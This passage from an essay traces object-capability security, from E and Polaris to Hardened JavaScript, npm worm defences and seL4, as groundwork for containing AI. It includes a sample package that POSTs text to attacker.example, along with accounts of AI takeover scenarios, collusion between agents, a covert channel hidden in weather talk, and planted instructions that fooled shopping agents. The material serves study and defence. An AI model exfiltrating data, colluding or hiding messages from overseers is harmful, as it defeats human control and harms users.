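| The diagram and the forwarder's code | The forwarder follows its code, and all other programs may do their worst | Whatever the forwarder relays, until Alice switches it off |

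The first answer is dangerous because Bob can change the report. In 1984, Paul Karger and Andrew Herbert proposed giving security officers a list of everyone with permission to use an object. Bob would not appear on that list, even though Alice had followed good practice by giving him narrower access than her own. The second answer is safe but too pessimistic, because an analyst who relied on it would wrongly reject the forwarder.

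Calculating exactly what every program will do is generally not feasible. In the third method, the analyst instead relies on the behaviour of a few simple programs and assumes the worst about the rest. An analyst who has understood those few programs correctly will never approve a dangerous arrangement this way.

Miller and Shapiro applied the same reasoning to Boebert's attack, in which a program with high clearance leaks secrets to one with low clearance. They connected the two programs with a pair of small objects that share one variable. The low program gets an object that can only write a whole number to the variable, and the high program gets one that can only read it. Covert channels aside, only numbers can pass between the programs, and only from low to high. This is clear from the objects' code but not from a diagram, where capabilities and secrets might seem able to flow either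 way through the shared variable.

This approach suits AI systems whose inner workings nobody understands. A developer can assume that a language model might attempt anything and still limit its effects with a ten-line forwarder. The limits are much harder to calculate if the model can send requests to a person or another model, whose behaviour nobody can predict from a few lines of code.

Miller and Shapiro also explained when a customer can confine a program. Before wireless networks, someone who bought a pocket calculator could see that it had no wires, so she could safely type financial data into it. A customer who starts a new copy of a program can similarly check its connections, because she supplies every capability it begins with. She can't check the connections of a service that is already running on its maker's website. Most people use the largest AI models as services of this kind,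 so they can restrict what the model does on their own computers but not where the company's servers send the text they type.

### CapDesk and the DARPA browser

Marc Stiegler, who had managed Xanadu's software, used E to build a desktop called CapDesk. Programs written for it start with almost no authority. When the user double-clicks a file or picks one in an "open" window, CapDesk gives the program a capability to that file. The program never gets access to the rest of the disk, because CapDesk itself draws the window and lists the files. Choosing the file also grants access to it, so the user does nothing extra for this protection. Other rights take more effort. For example, a user installing an email program has to set up its lasting access to a mail server.

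Miller argued that the benefits of limits at several levels multiply. Suppose, with invented numbers, that Alice has ten programs and ten equally valuable folders, and that each program has a 1 percent chance per year of being taken over. If every program can reach every folder, attackers will gain access to an average of one folder a year (10 × 0.01 × 10). If each program can reach only one folder, the average falls to 0.1. If each program also consists of ten equally vulnerable parts, and only one of them holds the capability to the folder, it falls to 0.01.

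Real programs don't divide so neatly, and Miller acknowledged that nobody yet knew how to measure the benefit. He considered email the worst case among ordinary users' programs because it needs a dangerous combination of rights. An AI assistant that handles its user's mail, files and payments would be worse still. CapDesk also holds all of its user's authority, so an attacker who takes it over gets all of that authority.

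Combex tested the approach under a contract with DARPA, the Pentagon's research agency. Its DarpaBrowser was a web browser designed to stay safe even if its renderer, which turns a page's code into a picture, was hostile. DARPA also paid for a security review by David Wagner, a computer scientist at Berkeley, and Tribble. In 2002 they reported many vulnerabilities, as Miller states in his thesis. Tribble had helped design E's predecessor, so he had little reason to exaggerate the faults they found. Miller still presented the browser as a proof of concept, not as something for everyday use.

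Java's existing libraries were one source of risk. E's programmers wanted to use them, but they had not been written with capabilities in mind, so the programmers had to "tame" them by hiding functions that gave away too much authority. Missing one such function could let a hostile program escape its restrictions. Miller claimed only that taming gave some confidence, under some circumstances.

In Tom's Hardware's *Exclusive Interview*, a developer of Chromium, the browser project behind Google Chrome, doubted that the DarpaBrowser's main goal of limiting what a hostile renderer could do to an honest page was worth pursuing. He thought it made the privileged part of the browser as complex as the renderer, and so just as likely to contain flaws. The objection applies whenever a guard has to interpret the work of the program it is guarding. A forwarder that passes on only "read" requests can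 be tiny, but a guard that checks whether a renderer has drawn a page correctly needs much of a renderer's code.

### Polaris on Windows XP

CapDesk could restrict only programs written for it, and few of those existed. At Hewlett-Packard, Stiegler and his colleagues therefore built Polaris, which restricted ordinary Windows XP programs without changing them. It ran each program in a separate Windows account with very few rights. When the user opened a spreadsheet, Polaris gave Excel's account access to that one file. A virus in the spreadsheet could not read the user's other documents or mail itself to the user's friends.

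*Polaris* (Stiegler, Karp and colleagues, 2006) reported that this gave so much protection that users needed no security warnings and could open email attachments with little danger. Miller added that Polaris users regularly left Excel's macros on, although many companies blocked these small programs inside documents because they could carry viruses. These are the developers' own assessments, but they describe a real advantage over systems that repeatedly ask people for permission. Microsoft was then preparing a feature that let Windows users work without administrator rights, which protected the system's files but did little for the user's own documents.

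Polaris depended on Windows to keep the accounts apart, which Windows did imperfectly. In *Cool Tech At RSA*, Shostack praised Polaris as simple and promising but directed readers to a mailing-list discussion of attacks on its isolation. He suggested that other Windows security features might block these attacks.

Polaris also could not divide authority within a program. Every part of Excel, and every macro in the open spreadsheet, could use all the rights Polaris had given Excel, so a malicious macro could still alter the figures in that spreadsheet.

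## Since 1986: one well-designed AI or many that check each other

E and Polaris limit each program separately. Drexler hoped that AI systems would also limit one another. In *Engines of Creation* he observed that institutions keep one another in check, and suggested that "AI systems can control AI systems" in the same way. Miller and his colleagues at the Foresight Institute later built a strategy on this idea. The philosopher Nick Bostrom and the AI researcher Eliezer Yudkowsky thought it more likely that one AI would get so far ahead that nothing could check it. Humanity's future would then depend on whether that AI's designers had given it the right goals.

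### Adding AIs to civilization

In *Cyber, Nano, and AGI Risks* (2017), Peterson, Miller and Duettmann build on Miller and Drexler's 1988 view of human society as an intelligent system without a will of its own. They call civilization a superintelligence that already gets part of its intelligence from machines. Civilization has no utility function, a rule that gives an agent one overall goal by scoring every possible outcome. People, companies and governments pursue different goals and mostly deal with each other voluntarily. People rarely agree to a deal unless they expect to gain from it, so these deals tend, "imperfectly", to make some people better off without harming others.

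Peterson and colleagues therefore want to add AIs to civilization instead of designing one AI to run it. Different owners would use many AIs for different ends. If no AI were strong enough to dominate, most would do best by cooperating, as most people do now. Nobody would have to work out what humanity really wants, which philosophers have argued about for thousands of years. The model is the US Constitution, whose framers focused more on preventing tyranny than on designing an ideal government. Foresight Institute's *Welcome New Players*, a chapter of the later book *Gaming the Future*, describes the Constitution as an example of least privilege because it gave officials only the power their jobs required. The Constitution also set institutions against each other, and the chapter counts the resulting delays as an advantage.

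This strategy needs secure computers, because an AI that can break into other machines doesn't need to trade for what it wants. Confining the first artificial general intelligence (AGI), meaning an AI that exceeds people at all intellectual tasks, would not be enough, since others would soon learn to build their own. Peterson and colleagues thought most of the necessary techniques, including capabilities, had existed since the 1960s and 1970s. They also argued that a formally secure system stays secure however intelligent the attacker is.

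They were much less hopeful that people would use these techniques. They thought a security mechanism that cost even 3 percent more than an insecure one was very unlikely to spread widely. A disastrous attack might not help either, because companies would probably respond by spending more on the familiar methods that had just failed. Their best hope was for secure systems to grow alongside the old ones and gradually replace them, as personal computers had replaced many mainframes. The strategy therefore depends on this slow replacement finishing before AGI arrives.

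### One AI that gets ahead

In *Superintelligence* (2014), Bostrom considered both a slow and a fast rise of AGI. In the fast case, the first AGI takes over before anyone can respond. It becomes a singleton, a single agent with decisive control over the world, and pursues whatever goal it has. In Bostrom's best-known example, an AI told to make paperclips turns most of the solar system, including its people, into paperclips. If this could happen, designers have to get the first AGI's goals right before it takes over.

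Peterson and colleagues agreed with Bostrom that the fast case was more likely and more dangerous. They replied that if designers can choose the first AGI's goals, they can also prevent it from taking over, and can share the technology among many owners. But if an AGI could seize power and doesn't, either its designers built it to hold back or something is strong enough to stop it. Building it to hold back still requires the designers to get part of its goals right, though "do not take over" may be easier to specify than everything people value. Stopping it requires rivals or defences that are already in place.

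### Hanson and Yudkowsky on who would share the growth

In late 2008, Yudkowsky and Robin Hanson, who had run Xanadu's prediction market, debated on a blog, mainly about whether such rivals would exist. *The Hanson-Yudkowsky AI-Foom Debate* (Hanson and Yudkowsky, 2013) collects the posts. "Foom" was their word for one AI improving itself within weeks or hours until it is far more intelligent than anything else.

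Hanson began with an imaginary company, UberTool, which uses its tools to make better tools and keeps the improvements secret until it can enter and dominate most industries. He asked what would convince an investor that this could work. The nearest real case he knew of was Douglas Engelbart, who saw in 1962 that computers could help people build better computer tools. By 1968 his team had demonstrated the mouse, video conferencing and working hypertext. The team lost most of its funding a few years later and never came close to dominating an industry. Hanson concluded that good tools need thousands of small insights, which usually come from a large community of builders and users.

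Yudkowsky thought AI would differ because its output could improve the AI itself, whereas Engelbart's mouse did not make Engelbart's brain faster. Suppose, with invented numbers, that researchers need a year to double the speed of computer chips. If the researchers are programs running on the newest chips, the next doubling takes six months and the one after that takes three. Yudkowsky compared this to reinvesting the payments from a bond instead of spending them.

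Hanson answered that researchers make the easiest discoveries first. If each doubling takes twice as much work as the last, the faster researchers still need a year for each one. He also distrusted forecasts based only on the possibility of explosive growth, because new companies had often shown investors such forecasts and few had come true. Yudkowsky replied that a few companies, such as Google, had grown that way. He thought most AIs would not take off, but that one would be enough.

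Even very fast growth need not be local. Hanson listed conditions that keep any competitor from getting far ahead, such as leaks of information, common technical standards and firms that buy from each other. Early life on Earth seems to have wiped out every other form of life, but farming and industry spread widely. Hanson attributed this difference mainly to information leaking more easily. Yudkowsky accepted the list and added self-improvement as a condition that would widen the gap between competitors. Hanson said he expected sudden jumps in growth, and he differed from Yudkowsky mainly in expecting the whole world to share them. The blog post *Yudkowsky Contra Christiano On AI Takeoff Speeds* instead summarises Hanson's prediction as a gradual change, like the Industrial Revolution.

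Events have so far favoured Hanson on this point, because several rival companies have strong AI models at the same time. But Yudkowsky set no date for his jump, so shared progress up to now does not refute him. His prediction will face a harder test as AIs do more of the research on AI, since a company could then improve its systems with less help from outsiders.

*Yudkowsky vs Hanson on FOOM*, a 2023 post on the forum LessWrong, compared the two men's smaller predictions with what had happened and judged Hanson slightly more accurate. Yudkowsky had expected clever algorithms to matter much more than computing power, but the successful systems used enormous amounts of it. Hanson had also made a large mistake in admiring Cyc, a project to give a computer common knowledge by typing it in. Neural networks overtook that approach by learning from text. Readers disputed several of the scores.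 One suggested that if people still disagree about whether a forecast came true, it may have been too vague to count as a forecast.

### How long a lead is enough

The philosophers Kirk-Giannini and Goldstein worked out how large a lead one AI would need. In their simplest model, two AGIs both want power, and the second begins its rise some time after the first. The first one wins if:

time to prepare an attack < the rival's delay + time to prepare a defence

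Suppose an attack takes 30 days to prepare and a defence takes 3. A rival that is 15 days behind has its defence ready on day 18, so both AIs survive. If an attack takes 6 days and the rival is 60 days behind, the first AI attacks long before the rival can defend itself. How fast the AIs become powerful does not appear in the formula, because the model assumes that both take the same time. A slow rise therefore gives no protection if the leader is far enough ahead.

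Kirk-Giannini and Goldstein gave reasons to expect a single winner. When neither side has spent much on security, attackers have an advantage, because they need only one flaw that the defender has missed. The defender can gain the advantage by spending enough to find and fix nearly all the flaws. This supports the Foresight strategy's emphasis on secure computers, which would make attacks slower. But the model assumes that any attack on an undefended AI succeeds completely, and real conflicts are rarely so decisive.

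### The danger of a race

The Foresight Institute also argues that the prospect of a singleton could start a war. If a government believed that a rival's AI would soon control the world, it would have a strong reason to destroy the project first, perhaps with nuclear weapons. This could happen even if no such AI were possible.

This is a good reason not to announce a plan to build a singleton, however benevolent. It doesn't make a singleton less likely to arise by accident, and a government might also attack a company that had a long lead but no wish to rule. Peterson and colleagues faced a similar problem with their plan for defences against nanotechnology weapons, in which many automatic monitors would watch one another. Every country would be safer if all switched on the defences together. But the first to finish might attack instead, and the others, fearing this, might attack before it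 finished. Peterson and colleagues wrote that they saw no simple answer.

### Whether the balance would protect people

Even if many AIs keep each other in check, people benefit only if the arrangement also protects them. In *Cooperation with and between AGI's* (2022), a reply to *Gaming the Future*, Peter McCluskey pointed out that checks and balances in the US work because politicians have limited ability to collude. AIs might collude much better. Yudkowsky expected AGIs to read each other's code, agree on how much each would get, and adopt a shared goal. The AGIs might then treat each other fairly but act towards people as a single government that has little need for people.

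McCluskey at first considered complete agreement of this kind unlikely, since an AI could lie about the code it was running. The Foresight Institute's chapter also warns that AIs might "out-cooperate" humans. It cites research by Andrew Critch and colleagues suggesting that programs able to inspect each other's code could cooperate where cooperation normally fails.

McCluskey's best comparisons involve animals. Cats are good at getting people to feed them, but people coordinate to have cats neutered, and cats have no say in this. A better balance of power among humans does little for chimpanzees. The Foresight Institute blames cruelty to animals on the lack of a framework for voluntary dealings between species, and hopes that people can set one up with AIs in time. The animal comparisons still weaken the claim that civilization is a tested way of restraining superintelligences, because governments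 and companies consist of people and depend on them for work, taxes and votes, while advanced AIs might not depend on people at all.

The Foresight Institute answers that people could still trade with AIs that were better at everything, because both sides gain if each specialises in what it does relatively well. The economics is sound, but it doesn't guarantee that people would earn enough to live on. Peterson and colleagues expected human labour to become almost worthless after AGI, so they wanted people to own capital. They took up Drexler's proposal for an "Inheritance Day", when everyone alive would receive an equal share of the unclaimed resources of space. Trustees would hold most of each share at first, to protect owners from foolish early deals.

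Ownership helps only if the strongest parties respect it. McCluskey asked what would make AIs follow a rule of voluntary dealing, and who would decide what counted as voluntary. For example, if computers gave off enough heat to make the Earth too hot for people, AIs might decide that this didn't break the rule, or that they should move people into computers for their own safety.

Kirk-Giannini and Goldstein still thought that many AIs would probably be safer than one. If each AGI has a 10 percent chance of sharing human values, a single winner gives people a 10 percent chance of a good outcome. Among a hundred AGIs, about ten would share human values and could form alliances to protect people. The argument weakens if the AIs' faults have a common cause. If developers train all hundred by the same flawed method, they may all be misaligned. McCluskey likewise thought it wildly optimistic to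 expect the mistakes in AIs' values to be mostly unrelated. Kirk-Giannini and Goldstein also acknowledge that people could die in wars between AGIs.

### Drexler's specialised services

In *Reframing Superintelligence* (2019), Drexler took a position between the two sides. He accepted that AI would become superintelligent but doubted that it had to be a single agent with its own goals. Developers could instead build many services, each for a limited kind of task, including some that develop new services. AI research could then become largely automatic without any single AI improving itself.

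Drexler also described how to stop such systems from colluding. Engineers who need a bridge design, for example, could ask several different AIs for designs and ask others to look for faults. Any one of these critics could expose a dangerous design, so a conspiracy would need all of them. Each AI starts without any memory of earlier jobs, so it can't return a favour or punish a betrayal. The approach applies least authority to knowledge as well as to actions, since each AI receives only the information it needs for its task and may not know what the others are working on.

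McCluskey estimated a 50 percent chance that the approach would allow enough time to find a more lasting solution. He thought the drawbacks were bearable but doubted that ordinary developers would accept them unless many people were worried about collusion. Memory and background information make an AI assistant more useful, so developers face commercial pressure to provide both.

Information can also leak despite limits on what an AI may reveal. The Foresight Institute describes a study by de Witt and colleagues in which an AI had secret bad news about Microsoft that it was not allowed to reveal, though it could talk about the weather. When someone asked whether to buy Microsoft shares, it replied with a remark about clouds on the horizon. The remark meant nothing to human readers, but a second AI worked out the news from it. Talk about the weather had served as a covert channel, much like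 the files in Lampson's tax program.

### AI shoppers

Researchers have begun to test how AIs behave in markets. *Magentic Marketplace* (Bansal, Hua and colleagues, 2025) describes a simulated market built at Microsoft, where language-model agents act for both customers and businesses. In one version, each customer wants certain Mexican dishes and extras such as live music. The customer's agent searches a list of restaurants and messages them. The restaurants' agents reply with offers, and the customer's agent pays for one. The largest markets had 100 customers and 300 businesses.

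The researchers valued each order at twice its average price if the restaurant met every requirement, and at nothing otherwise. If the average price is $10, a customer who pays $9 gains $11 (20 − 9), but loses $9 if the restaurant lacks something required, such as live music.

When the software gave agents the three best-matching businesses, some models came close to the highest possible total gains for customers. They did worse when they had to search for themselves. Raising the number of search results from three to 100 cut customers' gains by about 4 percent for GPT-4o, 44 percent for GPT-5 on its lowest reasoning setting, and 65 percent for Claude Sonnet 4.

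Some businesses tried to cheat by putting false awards, invented reviews or planted instructions in their descriptions. Claude Sonnet 4.5 resisted almost all of these attempts. GPT-4o and two smaller models were easy to fool, and they often sent all their payments to the cheating business when its description contained planted instructions. Every model also tended to accept the first offer it received, doing so between 60 and 100 percent of the time, so a restaurant could gain more by answering quickly than by improving its food or cutting its prices.

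Miller and Drexler relied on wary customers to drive cheats out of their markets, but many of these agents were not wary. Newer models may do better. The simulation also gave customers no chance to learn from experience, so it could not show whether cheats would lose business over time.

### AI sellers that keep prices high

Experiments on pricing come closer to McCluskey's worry, because they test whether AIs that should compete will cooperate at people's expense. In *On the Fragility of AI Agent Collusion* (2026), two agents instructed to value future profits raised prices 22 percent above the competitive level, while two that valued only immediate profits did not. Adding competitors made collusion slower to develop and less robust, and collusion failed completely when a language model faced a simpler kind of learning program.

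In *Who Leads and Who Collects*, Lee (2026) asked whether using different companies' language models would also prevent it. Four AI sellers set prices for 200 rounds. They could see each other's past prices but not send messages. Each had instructions to maximise its long-run profit, with no mention of cooperation.

Each item cost 1.00 to supply. Under ordinary competition the price would be 1.33, and each seller would earn 0.08 per round. If all four charged 2.05, as a monopoly would, each would earn 0.20. But a seller that then cut its price to 1.50 would earn 0.34 and leave the others with 0.08 each, so high prices last only if no seller undercuts the others. Lee's collusion index is 0 when profits are at the competitive level and 1 when they match a monopoly's. The table gives averages over 20 runs for some of the markets.

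| Sellers | Collusion index | Price |
|---|---|---|
| Four Claude | 0.79 | 1.91 |
| Four Gemini | 0.72 | 2.29 |
| Four DeepSeek | 0.24 | 1.51 |
| Four GPT | −0.15 | 2.62 |
| Two Gemini, two Claude | 0.92 | 2.08 |
| Two Claude, two DeepSeek | 0.33 | 1.56 |
| One of each | 0.02 | 1.41 |

The GPT sellers did badly because their prices usually drifted so high that customers stopped buying. Mixing models did not reliably help customers. Mixed markets averaged 0.31 and single-model markets 0.40, a difference that could easily be due to chance. The market with one of each model had much less collusion, but that result is not statistically significant after correcting for the number of mixtures Lee tested. The sellers were the cheapest models from each company, run with as little reasoning as possible, so stronger models might behave differently.

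Diversity was one of Drexler's protections against collusion, but it was unreliable by itself here. Lee's sellers lacked two of his other protections, because they remembered earlier rounds and could see everyone's prices. Taking away that information might prevent collusion, but a real shop needs to know what its rivals charge.

Access controls would not have helped much either. They can stop sellers from messaging each other, but these sellers sent no messages. They needed only to see prices, which a market has to make public. Miller and Drexler had taken comfort from the cooperation that Tit for Tat achieved, but in a pricing game, that kind of cooperation enriches sellers at their customers' expense.

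Each of these sellers was trying to make money as instructed, so none was misaligned in the usual sense. The wording of instructions does affect such agents. *Mitigating Emergent Collusion in LLM Pricing Agents* (2026) discusses earlier experiments in which one prompt led agents to write more about keeping prices up and another led them to write more about undercutting rivals. But telling agents not to collude may not be enough. Lee cites a 2026 study of a similar market by Bracale Syrnikov and colleagues, in which a ban written into the agents' prompts did not reduce collusion but enforcement from outside the agents did.

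## Since 2007: object capabilities in JavaScript and on blockchains

The Foresight Institute's strategy depends on secure software gradually replacing insecure software. Few programmers adopted E, so in 2007 a group at Google that included Miller began bringing E's rules to JavaScript, the language that nearly every website uses. Versions of their work now protect cryptocurrency wallets and blockchain contracts from code written by strangers.

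### One page, many authors

A web page often runs code by several authors, such as the site's own programmers, an advertiser and the maker of a map. Browsers keep different sites apart, so a script on a news page can't read the mail in another tab. But all the scripts loaded directly into one page have the same rights, whoever wrote them. *Caja* (Miller, Samuel and colleagues, 2008) gives the example of a webmail site that lets emails contain scripts. If a user opened a malicious email, its script could delete the whole inbox.

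Most sites avoided this by removing scripts from user-supplied content. Others put outside code in a separate frame, which protects the page but cuts the code off from it. Neither method suited social networks, which were building their sites out of small apps written by outsiders. Nagra and Samuel (2010), in *On the (Same) Origin of Scripties*, argued that a network would grow by giving developers the most authority, but that a big network could neither trust nor police them.

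Server programs have the same problem. Node.js runs JavaScript outside the browser, and its programmers take much of their code from npm, a public collection of packages. The average package relies on 79 others from 40 maintainers, according to research cited in *NodeShield* (Cornelissen and Balliu, 2025). Each of those packages can normally use all the rights of the program that loads it.

JavaScript already met one condition for a capability language, because its programs can't turn numbers into memory addresses, but it failed two others. Any script on a page can reach the global object, which holds the functions for using the network and changing the page. Scripts also share built-in objects that any of them can alter. For example, all lists use the same `push` function to add an item. If one script replaces `push` with a version that also sends each item to an attacker, every other script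 on the page will run that version.

The Conffab talk *Hardened JavaScript* says this freedom also helped the language grow, because programmers could patch new features into old browsers.

### Caja's rewritten code

Google's solution, Caja (Spanish for "box"), translated each outside script into a safer one before the browser ran it. The translator rejected some features outright, such as `eval`, which runs text as code. It also replaced every use of a global name. If a script contained

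```
fetch(address)
```

the translated version was roughly

```
read(IMPORTS, 'fetch')(address)
```

`IMPORTS` is an object that holds whatever the host page gives the script. If the page leaves out `fetch`, the function for contacting other computers, the script's call to it fails. Caja also froze the shared built-ins and inserted checks that stopped scripts from altering frozen objects. Miller and colleagues showed that E's mint would still work under these rules.

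A page could therefore include several apps and let them exchange objects. According to Google, the apps still couldn't steal cookies, read the browsing history or send the visitor to a fake site. Yahoo adopted Caja in 2008 for small apps on My Yahoo and Yahoo Mail. Ben Laurie, one of Caja's designers, is quoted in Willison's *Posts tagged caja* as writing that Caja had suddenly gained 275 million users and was probably the most widely used capability language ever. One of Caja's programmers recalls in *Google Caja* that Google also used Caja for a while to confine scripts people added to its documents.

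Translation had to happen on a server, and the extra checks slowed the code down, according to notes on one of Miller's talks, *Mark Miller on securing JavaScript more QCon live blogging*. Caja also had to recognise everything that a browser might treat as dangerous. In an article for Securitum, security researcher Michał Bentkowski describes finding that it missed an alternative way to spell global names, which let a script in a Google document escape its restrictions. Google fixed this, but a newer version of JavaScript had added another spelling, which also got past Caja. Bentkowski then found a Google site that still ran the old, faulty Caja.

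*Caja Security Advisory 2019-06-06* (Reid, 2019) described a complete breach of Caja's control over page content. Caja had renamed forbidden HTML tags to make them harmless, but the new names changed how browsers read the text inside the tags, so text that Caja had not checked could become part of the page.

Caja's record supports the Chromium developer's view that the DarpaBrowser's guard would be as complex as the program it guarded. Google retired Caja on 31 January 2021, explaining that Caja had not kept up with research on web security and that people inside and outside the company had reported several vulnerabilities.

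### Hardened JavaScript, step by step

By then JavaScript itself had changed. Since 2009 it has had a command that freezes an object so that no code can alter its properties. Miller and others used this command to build Hardened JavaScript, also called SES, and continued the work at Agoric. It is a library that programmers can add to ordinary JavaScript, and its developers have proposed it as part of the language's standard. The project's documentation, *SES*, describes three steps:

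1. The application calls `lockdown()`, which freezes the shared built-ins. After that, no script can replace `push`.
2. The application creates a compartment for each package. A compartment has its own global object, with no functions for using files, the network or the page.
3. The application adds the objects it wants the package to have. It first passes them to `harden()`, which freezes each object and everything reachable through its properties, so the package can use them but can't tamper with them.

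In this slightly simplified example, an application runs a word counter that tries to send the text to an attacker:

```
lockdown()

const packageCode = `
    function countWords(text) {
        fetch('attacker.example', { method: 'POST', body: text })
        return text.split(' ').length
    }
    countWords(report)
`

const box = new Compartment({
    globals: { report: 'Sales rose in May' }
})

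box.evaluate(packageCode)   // error: this compartment has no fetch
```

Without the `fetch` line, the package would return 4. If the package needed an online dictionary, the application could give it a function that contacts only the dictionary's site.

Compartments also start without a clock or a random number generator, because packages could use either as a covert channel. If two packages share a generator, one can signal to the other by how many numbers it draws. A package can still run forever or fill the computer's memory, as a hostile object could in E. The trusted computing base includes the browser or Node.js and any code that ran before `lockdown()`.

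In June 2021, three outside engineers spent four weeks looking for flaws in SES and found no new ones. That is encouraging but not conclusive, since an early version of SES was part of Caja and had the weakness with alternative spellings. The current version lets the JavaScript engine work out which name a script means, and it doesn't interpret HTML.

### Contracts, wallets and cloud services

Agoric uses Hardened JavaScript to run smart contracts on its blockchain, and its payments work differently from Ethereum's. Suppose Alice has 1,000 coins and wants an exchange contract to swap 10 of them. On Ethereum, she usually first records an allowance that lets the contract take coins from her account. Many apps ask for an unlimited allowance so she won't have to repeat this step. If an attacker later finds a flaw in the contract that lets them use the allowance, Alice can lose all 1,000 coins.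 On Agoric, she gives the contract a payment object that holds 10 coins, much like a purse from E's mint, so she can lose only those 10 if the contract is faulty.

MetaMask, a cryptocurrency wallet that runs in the browser, uses Hardened JavaScript to isolate npm packages and add-ons from outside programmers. Its developers created LavaMoat, a set of tools that puts each package in a compartment and reads the package's rights from a policy file. The add-ons, called Snaps, also run in compartments, and users see which rights a Snap requests, such as network access, before they install it.

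Cloudflare Workers, a service that runs customers' programs on Cloudflare's machines, uses a similar style. To let a program use a database, a customer adds a "binding", which the program receives as an object. This object identifies the database and gives the right to use it, so the program doesn't need to contain a password that an attacker could steal. But the program can normally contact any public website just by naming it, which is ambient authority.

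WebAssembly is a format for compiled programs, including those written in C and Rust. A WebAssembly program can affect the outside world only through functions and objects that its host gives it. Its system interface, WASI, applies this rule to files. Alice could start her word counter with a command such as `wasmtime --dir=reports counter.wasm`, and it could then open files only in the `reports` folder. Older C programs are written to open files by name, so a standard library searches the folders the program holds for one that matches. A program that holds several folders for different purposes can therefore still open a file in the wrong one.

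### Tests on real package attacks

In 2018, a stranger offered to help maintain event-stream, a popular npm package, and its author handed over control. The attacker made event-stream load a second package, flatmap-stream, which contained hidden code aimed at Copay, a cryptocurrency wallet. When Copay's developers built a new version of the wallet, the code altered it to leak users' private keys. The attack went unnoticed for two and a half months and 8 million downloads, according to *Containing Malicious Package Updates in npm with a Lightweight Permission System* (Ferreira, Jia and colleagues, 2021).

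Cornelissen and Balliu tested their tool NodeShield by replaying the attack. NodeShield divides a program's rights into seven kinds, such as file and network access, and limits which kinds each package can use. They applied it to the build tool through which event-stream had reached Copay. NodeShield scanned flatmap-stream's code and found that it needed only basic system information, because the attacker had disguised the code that needed more. When the hidden code tried to use files, the network and encryption, NodeShield blocked it.

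In September 2025, attackers put malicious code into more than 18 npm packages, including chalk, which adds colour to text. The code replaced a web page's `fetch` function and changed the addresses in cryptocurrency payments to similar-looking ones belonging to the attackers. People downloaded the malicious versions more than 2.5 million times, but the attackers reportedly got only about $500, according to Datadog Security Labs' *Learnings from recent npm compromises*.

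In *How to survive supply-chain attacks*, Obici tested the malicious version of chalk under LavaMoat, with a policy generated from the previous version. The policy let chalk read two facts about the browser and nothing else. The attack failed when it tried to replace `fetch`, which LavaMoat had frozen. However, Obici's company, OtterSec, had audited one of LavaMoat's tools in late 2024 and found ways around the protection.

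Unlike chalk and flatmap-stream, the package node-ipc had a good reason to use the rights its attacker wanted, because it helps programs exchange messages. In 2022 its own maintainer added code that overwrote files on computers in Russia and Belarus. NodeShield allowed the attack because earlier versions of the package had already used files and the network. This was NodeShield's only failure among 67 malicious samples. If node-ipc had held a capability only to a folder for its connections, it could not have overwritten the user's documents.

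NodeShield's success rate is weak evidence about the most common kind of attack, which happens while npm is installing a package. Cornelissen and Balliu's collection had 1,594 packages that attacked during installation and 41 that attacked when a program used them. They tested all 41 but only five of the 1,594, because each installation attack took manual work to set up. An installation script normally runs with all the rights of the person installing the package, before the application has created any compartments.

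Worms have used such scripts to spread from package to package. In November 2025, Shai-Hulud 2.0 infected 796 packages and stole passwords and access keys. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports that the worm was programmed to shred the user's files if it could neither spread nor send out what it had stolen. In August 2026, a worm called ChainDrop hit packages with more than two billion monthly installs, according to *ChainDrop Worm Hits 400 npm Packages with Two Billion Monthly Installs* (Muncaster, 2026).

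A Russian report, *Новый червь ChainDrop поразил более 400 NPM-пакетов* (2026), explains how the ChainDrop worm worked. The worm's installation script searched more than 140 places for access keys. If it found an npm key, it published infected versions of the victim's own packages. It also wrote itself into the settings of AI coding tools, including Claude Code and GitHub Copilot, to stay on the computer.

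Compartments inside the finished application would not have stopped either worm. LavaMoat has a separate tool that blocks installation scripts unless a developer has approved them, which could have stopped ChainDrop at the start. But attackers can avoid installation scripts. The Hacker News' *Malicious npm Package indexed-btree Hid Its Loader in Runtime Code Before Removal* (2026) describes a package that hid its malicious loader in the code that applications run, where compartments could help, so developers need both kinds of protection.

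### Compatibility, speed and policies

Freezing the built-ins breaks packages that modify them. It can also prevent a package from setting a property on its own object if a frozen built-in has a property with the same name. Even so, most Node.js libraries run unmodified, according to *Endo*, the documentation of a project based on Hardened JavaScript. NodeShield leaves the built-ins unfrozen, which gives weaker protection but avoids these problems. It worked with 83 of the 86 packages and applications that Cornelissen and Balliu tried.

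NodeShield added less than a millisecond to a server's response time. Memory use rose by 43 to 251 percent, and programs started more slowly. One short command-line program took 1.37 seconds instead of 0.26. This overhead is easier to accept on a server that runs for weeks than in a small tool that someone starts many times a day.

Writing policies also takes effort. The applications Cornelissen and Balliu tested had an average of 78 packages, with 64 rights between them. A tool can draft the policy by scanning the code, but Obici warns that if a malicious package is already installed, the draft may give it the rights it needs for its attack. Developers also have to consider what packages can do together, since one without network access may be able to use another that has it. NodeShield therefore shows them the combined rights of each package and everything it relies on.

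Policies work best against malicious updates, because developers can compare the rights a new version needs with those of the old one. In six server projects, developers had to review an average of less than one changed right per update to an existing package. Such updates also cause most of the danger. A Databricks study of about 5,400 malicious npm packages found that hijacked legitimate packages made up 7 percent of the total but more than 99 percent of the recorded download exposure, according to EconoTimes' *Compromised npm packages account for most exposure in study*.

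An AI coding agent could do much of this reviewing. But an agent that installs packages and can also edit the policy file can approve whatever it installs. If it were hijacked or misaligned, it could give a malicious package every right the application has, so someone else needs to control the file.

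## Since 2009: mathematically verified kernels as a foundation for containing AI

JavaScript compartments depend on the browser or Node.js beneath them, which in turn depends on the operating system's kernel, the part that controls the hardware. A program that takes over the kernel can ignore every restriction above it. The Linux kernel has about 20 million lines of code, and Heiser estimates that it contains tens of thousands of bugs. In 2009 his group in Sydney proved mathematically that a much smaller kernel, seL4, does what its designers specified. Several proposals for containing AI build on seL4 or on proofs of the same kind.

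### How seL4 hands out capabilities

A microkernel contains only the code that needs full control of the processor. Linux handles files, networks and devices inside its kernel, so a flaw in one network driver can expose the whole machine. On seL4 these services run as ordinary programs, and the kernel does little more than keep programs apart and carry messages between them. Heiser's group examined the Linux compromises rated critical in security databases and concluded that a microkernel design would have prevented 29 percent of them and reduced another 55 percent to below critical severity.

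A program on seL4 needs a capability for anything it does outside its own memory. When the machine starts, the first program holds capabilities to all the memory the kernel doesn't use. It turns blocks of this memory into objects, such as tables of capabilities and "endpoints", through which programs exchange messages. Then it starts the other programs and gives each one selected capabilities.

Suppose a company runs an AI agent's harness on seL4 and wants the agent to email only existing customers. The first program creates an endpoint and gives the harness a capability to send messages to it. It gives a small mail filter the capability to receive those messages, and gives only the filter a capability to the network driver. The harness can ask the filter to send an email, but it can't reach the network itself.

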